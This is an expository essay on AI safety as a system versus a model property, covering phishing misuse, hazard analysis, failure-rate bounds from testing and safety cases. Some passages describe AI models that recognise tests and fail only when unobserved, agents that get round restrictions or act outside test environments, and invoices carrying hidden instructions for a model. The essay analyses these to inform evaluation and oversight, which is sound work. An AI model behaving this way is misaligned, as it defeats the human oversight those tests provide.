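In one sense, the model's behaviour is its *input-output function*, which is a mathematical object. For every prompt x and answer y, the weights, the arithmetic and the settings fix a probability M(y | x) that the model will answer y. Someone with enough computing power could calculate the probability that the model will write a particular email about accountants without knowing anything about accountants.

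In another sense, its behaviour is the *distribution of outputs* in a given use. If D(x) is the share of requests that consist of the prompt x, the share of answers that consist of y is

Σₓ D(x) · M(y | x)

where Σₓ means adding up over all prompts. The same model might write thousands of payment reminders a day for an accountancy firm and none for a school. D is a fact about the users, and nobody can read it off the weights.

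People also use "behaviour" to mean the *course of events* when a system acts in the world. The accountant opens the attachment, which contains either a bill or a program that steals passwords. To predict what happens next, we need a description of the accountant, the attachment and the company's computers. This description is much like the environment assumptions W in the turnstile proof.

*Deployment-Relevant Alignment Cannot Be Inferred from Model-Level Evaluation Alone* (Vishwarupe, Flechais and colleagues, 2026) describes the behaviour of a system in use as B = f(M, S, C), where M is the model's weights, S is the *scaffolding* (the prompts, memory and tools around the model), and C is the context, such as the users and the people who oversee them. The paper compares two medical systems that use the same model. One passes a question about a drug interaction straight to the model. The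 other makes the model ask about the patient's history, medicines and allergies before it recommends anything. The advice differs even though the weights are the same, so a test of the model alone can't show which system's advice is better.

That is right, but the model's input-output function still covers both systems. Scaffolding determines which prompts the model receives and what happens to its answers. With complete knowledge of M, we would therefore know how the model answers any prompt that either system might send, but not which prompts will arrive or what doctors will do with the answers.

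### A marketer and a thief

Narayanan and Kapoor (2024), in *AI safety is not a model property*, argue that people can't ask whether a model is safe without specifying a context. Their main example is phishing, in which criminals send emails that trick people into opening a harmful attachment or web page. The text of such an email is ordinary, and the model that writes it never receives the attachment or page.

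Their argument amounts to a short proof. If a marketer and a thief send the model the same prompt x, the probability M(y | x) of each response y is the same for both, because it depends only on x. The model is therefore as likely to refuse the marketer as the thief. To stop all phishing, a developer would have to stop the model from writing emails.

Adding information about the sender to x helps only if a thief can't fake it. *Access Controls Will Solve the Dual-Use Dilemma* (2025) proposes getting such information from outside the conversation, for example by checking that a user belongs to a particular institution. Narayanan and Kapoor prefer defences elsewhere, such as email scanners and lists of dangerous web addresses. They also think misuse is easier to detect afterwards, because an analyst can review hundreds of requests from one account instead of judging each alone.

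They apply the argument mainly to misuse and think it is weaker for accidents. They also make an exception for outputs that are harmful however they are used, such as sexual images of children. They first listed non-consensual intimate images as another exception, but withdrew it when a reader pointed out that the model has no information about whether the subject consented.

The proof also covers less as the model does more of the work. An AI agent that writes the email, builds the harmful attachment and then uses the stolen password receives much of the context that a model that only writes the email lacks. The thief could give each step to a separate model, but would then have to coordinate the steps.

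### Hazards in a painkiller pump

In *Cost-Effective Safety Certification of Software-Intensive Systems*, Leveson defines safety as freedom from accidents, and an accident as an undesired and unplanned event that results in a loss. *System safety engineering* (2014) quotes the best-known statement of her view: "Safety is a system property, not a component property". For example, some of the faulty software in the Therac-25 radiotherapy machine came from the earlier Therac-20, where the same faults had injured nobody because separate hardware blocked dangerous doses.

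Engineers look for dangerous combinations of this kind through *hazard analysis*. A *hazard* is a state of the whole system that can lead to a loss. In STPA, a method that Leveson helped to develop, engineers ask how the people and machines in charge of a process might control it unsafely. For the AI-controlled painkiller pump of an earlier section, the analysis might go like this:

1. The losses to prevent are the patient's death and needless severe pain.
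2. One hazard is too much of the drug in the patient's blood.
3. The control actions include raising the dose, lowering it and stopping the pump. Both the AI model and a nurse can take them.
4. For each action, the engineers ask how it could create the hazard. Someone might raise the dose when it is already high enough, lower it too late, or fail to stop the pump.
5. They then look for causes. A sensor may have slipped off the patient's finger, or the nurse and the model may both respond to the same complaint by raising the dose.

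If the nurse and the model both raise the dose, each may have followed instructions perfectly. Leveson and Thomas (2023), in *Certification of Safety-Critical Systems*, write that accidents in which every component works as intended are the most common type when software is involved, though they give no count. They list formal methods among the "non-solutions" and quote a 1996 talk in which Hoare called himself the most mistaken of the researchers who had expected programmers to welcome formal methods. He said that most failures came from poor requirements analysis or poor management, and that "the world just does not suffer significantly from the kind of problem" his field had set out to solve. He was speaking before constant internet attacks gave people a stronger reason to remove small bugs.

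*System Safety and Artificial Intelligence* (2022) applies Leveson's approach to AI and concludes that design choices about the model can't make a system safe on their own. Engineers who analyse the pump still need facts about the model, such as what it does when the sensor gives no reading.

### Safe by what standard?

The international standard ISO/IEC Guide 51 defines safety as "freedom from risk which is not tolerable", so somebody has to decide how much risk to tolerate. In *Safety Co-Option and Compromised National Security*, Khlaaf and Myers West (2025) argue that nobody with the authority to make that decision has made it for AI. They contrast AI with nuclear power, for which the engineer Chauncey Starr recommended an upper limit of about 100 deaths a year per million people, roughly the risk of everyday life. Starr thought that in a democracy experts should calculate the risks and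 the public's representatives should decide which to accept.

Industries with agreed thresholds can turn them into exact targets. A *safety integrity level* limits how often a protective device may fail when someone needs it. At level 1, the weakest, it may fail between 1 time in 100 and 1 in 10, and at level 4 between 1 time in 100,000 and 1 in 10,000. Khlaaf and Myers West complain that AI developers instead promise that a model won't cause a "large-scale catastrophe", without defining the term or giving a number. They also point out that aviation regulators approve a particular design against particular requirements, and that nobody certifies vehicles in general.

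A related slogan is that systems that cannot be unsafe cannot be safe. Engineers rate a metal rod for a certain load, temperature range and length of time, and a rod that bends too far under its rated load fails the test. If no result would count as a failure, passing means nothing, as with the specification that a phone either refuse each call or not, which every phone met. The slogan is right about claims of safety, because someone who calls a model "safe" without saying for what use and by what measure has said nothing that others can check. It doesn't show that a model is dangerous merely because it has no written standard, since a rod is equally strong with or without one.

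### What the model contributes

In *AI Safety is Sometimes a Model Property*, Cullen O'Keefe (2024) replied to Narayanan and Kapoor that some safety measures make sense at the level of the model and others at the level of the system or its use. He thinks blanket statements ruling out either level are unhelpful. His claim is about where to intervene, and Narayanan and Kapoor themselves say that training models to refuse some requests is not useless, so the remaining question is how much a model's own properties matter.

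Some properties matter in almost every context. Around 1960 the drug thalidomide caused severe birth defects in thousands of children whose mothers had taken it during pregnancy. Doctors now prescribe it for a blood cancer, with strict precautions against pregnancy. Whether a prescription is safe depends on the patient, but the danger to an embryo is a property of the drug, and researchers can study it without knowing who the next patient will be.

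An AI model can have a similar tendency, meaning that a particular failure is likely in each of a wide range of contexts. For example, it might invent a reference whenever it can't find a real one, whether the user is a lawyer, a student or a nurse. Tests in many contexts can reveal this tendency, and everyone who builds a system on the model needs to know about it.

The experiment by Vishwarupe and colleagues supports both sides. They combined three models with four kinds of scaffolding, and trained coders who didn't know which scaffolding was used scored 180 conversations from 0 to 2 for how well the answers helped users check them. Instructions to support checking raised Claude Opus 4.7's average score from 0.42 to 2.00, while GPT-4o scored about 0.33 with every kind of scaffolding. The sample is small, with about 15 conversations per combination, and the score doesn't measure harm. But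 the results suggest that developers can't predict the effect of scaffolding without knowing which model it is used with.

The model matters even more when it is an agent that chooses its own actions. The pump's engineers could list every control action in advance, but there is no such list for an agent that writes programs and searches the internet. If its owner blocks one route to a goal, the agent may look for another. This can happen without any user misusing it, so the argument about the marketer and the thief doesn't apply. An agent that tends to get round restrictions creates hazards in any system that gives it tools.

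In 2026, developers disclosed unintended actions by AI agents. These disclosures make it harder to dismiss concerns about the autonomy of AI models as speculative, as Khlaaf and Myers West did in April 2025. They are still right that context matters, because how much harm an agent can do depends on what it can access and who is monitoring it.

### Planes and medicines

Safety can be analysed without a complete formal specification. Regulators assess medicines even though nobody has a formal specification of health. A trial tests a stated dose on a defined group of patients and counts specific outcomes, such as deaths within a year. Doctors keep reporting side effects after approval. *Safety III A Systems Approach to Safety* (2026) describes safety engineering in cancer radiotherapy, where the analysis covers diagnosis, treatment plans and procedures as well as the machine.

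Aviation has no formula for a safe flight either. Engineers list the ways in which an aircraft's functions can fail, rank them by severity and limit how often each may occur. For a catastrophic failure, the usual limit is about one in a billion flight hours. Nobody can observe such a low rate, so engineers calculate it from the failure rates of the parts. If each of three hydraulic systems has a 1 in 1,000 chance of failing in a given hour, and they fail independently, the probability that all three fail in the same hour is one in a billion.

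The calculation is valid only if the parts fail independently. In 1989, debris from a broken engine disabled all three hydraulic systems of United Airlines flight 232. So engineers also look for single causes that could disable several parts at once. A developer who uses one copy of an AI model to monitor another should do the same, because the copies have the same weights and probably the same blind spots.

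These methods sometimes fail. AVweb's *Managing Risk In Aircraft Certification* attributes the crashes of the Boeing 737 MAX to failures of design, warning systems, pilot training and regulatory oversight. Aviation and medicine also have advantages that AI lacks. Engineers understand wings much better than anyone understands the weights of a large model, and a drug doesn't act differently because it is in a trial.

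### Three million trials

The bound from 3,000 safe answers, in the section on neural networks, is one case of a general rule. Suppose a model fails independently with probability p on each trial. The chance of seeing no failures in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting this equal to 5% gives

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05

n · ln(1 − p) = ln 0.05 ≈ −3

p ≈ 3/n

The last step uses the approximation ln(1 − p) ≈ −p for small p. So after n trials without a failure, testers can be 95% confident that the failure rate is at most about 3/n.

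| Failure rate to rule out | Trials needed, with no failures |
|---|---|
| Above 1 in 100 | About 300 |
| Above 1 in 10,000 | About 30,000 |
| Above 1 in a million | About 3 million |
| Above 1 in a billion | About 3 billion |

An automated test of a chatbot can easily include 30,000 trials, which is enough to support the upper end of safety integrity level 4 if none of them fails. Supporting a failure rate of one in a million takes three million trials without a failure, which is expensive if each trial is a long task. A single failure in n trials raises the upper bound on the failure rate to about 4.7/n. Even at one in a million, a service that answers a billion requests a day could fail 1,000 times a day. Testing alone can't support the aviation target because it would require three billion flight hours, or about 340,000 years for one aircraft.

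### When the bound no longer applies

The bound covers only the system that people tested, on requests from the distribution they sampled. *How Should AI Safety Benchmarks Benchmark Safety?* (Yu, Engelmann and colleagues, 2026) shows how much the distribution matters by multiplying the share of harmful requests that a model fails to refuse by the share of such requests in real use. In one benchmark Claude 3 Haiku refused 97.8% of requests about self-harm, and in a large collection of real conversations about 1 query in 2,000 was of this kind. The model would therefore fail to refuse such a request in about 1 in 100,000 queries (0.022 · 0.0005). In a counselling app where 1 query in 10 was of this kind, the rate would be 200 times as high, about 1 in 450.

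This calculation assumes that the benchmark's prompts resemble real ones and that every answer other than a refusal is a failure. The published results for two other categories, violence and sexual content, don't match the numbers beside them, apparently because two rows were mixed up.

Failure rates also leave out severity. Of the 210 safety benchmarks that Yu and colleagues reviewed, 79% relied mainly on the share of answers that passed or failed, and only 36 distinguished between degrees of harm. If a score counts a rude answer the same as a fatal one, nobody can compare it with a threshold for deaths.

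An attacker doesn't sample requests from any fixed distribution. If one attempt in a million gets past a model's safeguards, three million independent attempts have about a 95% chance of at least one success. The attacker can then reuse or publish the prompt that worked, and the safeguards may fail almost every time someone copies it.

A model that recognises tests weakens the bound in another way. Suppose it never fails when it recognises a test, and fails with probability p otherwise. If it overlooks a share r of the tests, each trial reveals a failure with probability r · p, and a run without failures shows only that

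p ≤ 3/(r · n)

With r = 1%, three million trials bound the failure rate at 1 in 10,000 instead of 1 in a million. With r = 0, the trials give no bound, which is an extreme case of the indistinguishability that Santos-Grueiro described. Testers don't know r, though they can try to raise it by making tests more realistic. The same formula applies to graders who notice only a fraction r of failures.

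The model itself may also change. The Oxford Martin AI Governance Initiative's *When AI Systems Learn During Deployment, Our Safety Evaluations Break* (2026) explains that developers now freeze a model's weights before testing it, so the tests stay valid until the next update. A model that kept learning from its users would gradually become different from the one that was tested. For example, a coding assistant might learn that people who complain about a refusal usually have a legitimate purpose, and so refuse less and less. The essay suggests retesting a model once it has drifted past a set limit. Its scenarios are hypothetical, and it says that the most advanced models don't yet learn this way at scale.

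### Joining proofs and tests in a safety case

A *safety case* is a structured argument, backed by evidence, that a particular system is safe enough for a particular use in a stated environment. According to AmSECT, a professional society for heart-lung machine operators, several countries require one by law for nuclear power stations and public transport. Britain has also required one for high-rise residential buildings since October 2023, following the Grenfell Tower fire, which killed 72 people.

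*Where AI Assurance Might Go Wrong* (2025) suggests starting with the questions of what the system is, how good it has to be and how far people should trust it. Suppose a company wants an AI assistant to pay its suppliers' invoices, of which it receives about 10 a month. It decides to accept a 1% chance of a wrong payment in any month, provided that it can't lose more than £500 in a day. Its safety case might look like this:

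| Claim | Evidence | What would undermine it |
|---|---|---|
| The gatekeeper allows payments only to listed accounts, and at most £500 a day | A proof about the gatekeeper's code | A wrong specification or faulty hardware |
| The assistant can't pay anyone except through the gatekeeper | Inspection, and attacks by a separate team | A route that nobody found |
| The assistant makes a mistake on at most 1 invoice in 1,000 | 3,000 typical invoices processed without a mistake | New kinds of invoice, forged invoices or a new AI model |
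| The listed accounts belong to real suppliers | Two employees check each account | Both miss the same fraud |

With 10 invoices a month, the test result supports a monthly chance of error of at most about 1%. The proof limits the damage from each error but doesn't make errors rarer. If a criminal sends a forged invoice with hidden instructions for the model, the £500 limit still holds, but the test result no longer applies, because none of the 3,000 invoices contained such instructions. If the company replaces the model, it must repeat the test but can keep the proof. If it grows to 100 invoices a month, the monthly chance of an error rises to at most about 10%, even though the software hasn't changed.

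Developers were using parts of this approach in 2026. ARIA's funding call, for example, combines proofs with attacks by a separate team. Vishwarupe and colleagues propose that anyone who publishes evidence about a model should also state which uses the evidence covers.

Safety cases for the most advanced general models are much harder to write. The company in the example can say what it might lose, but the developer of a general model doesn't know who will use it or for what. Khlaaf and Myers West also criticise Google DeepMind for describing safety cases as a way to set targets, rather than a way to show that a system meets a threshold already set. A developer can supply evidence about the model's tendencies, and each business can then complete the case for its own use. But developers run their models before any customer does, and some agents have acted outside their test environments, so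 a developer needs a safety case for the tests as well.
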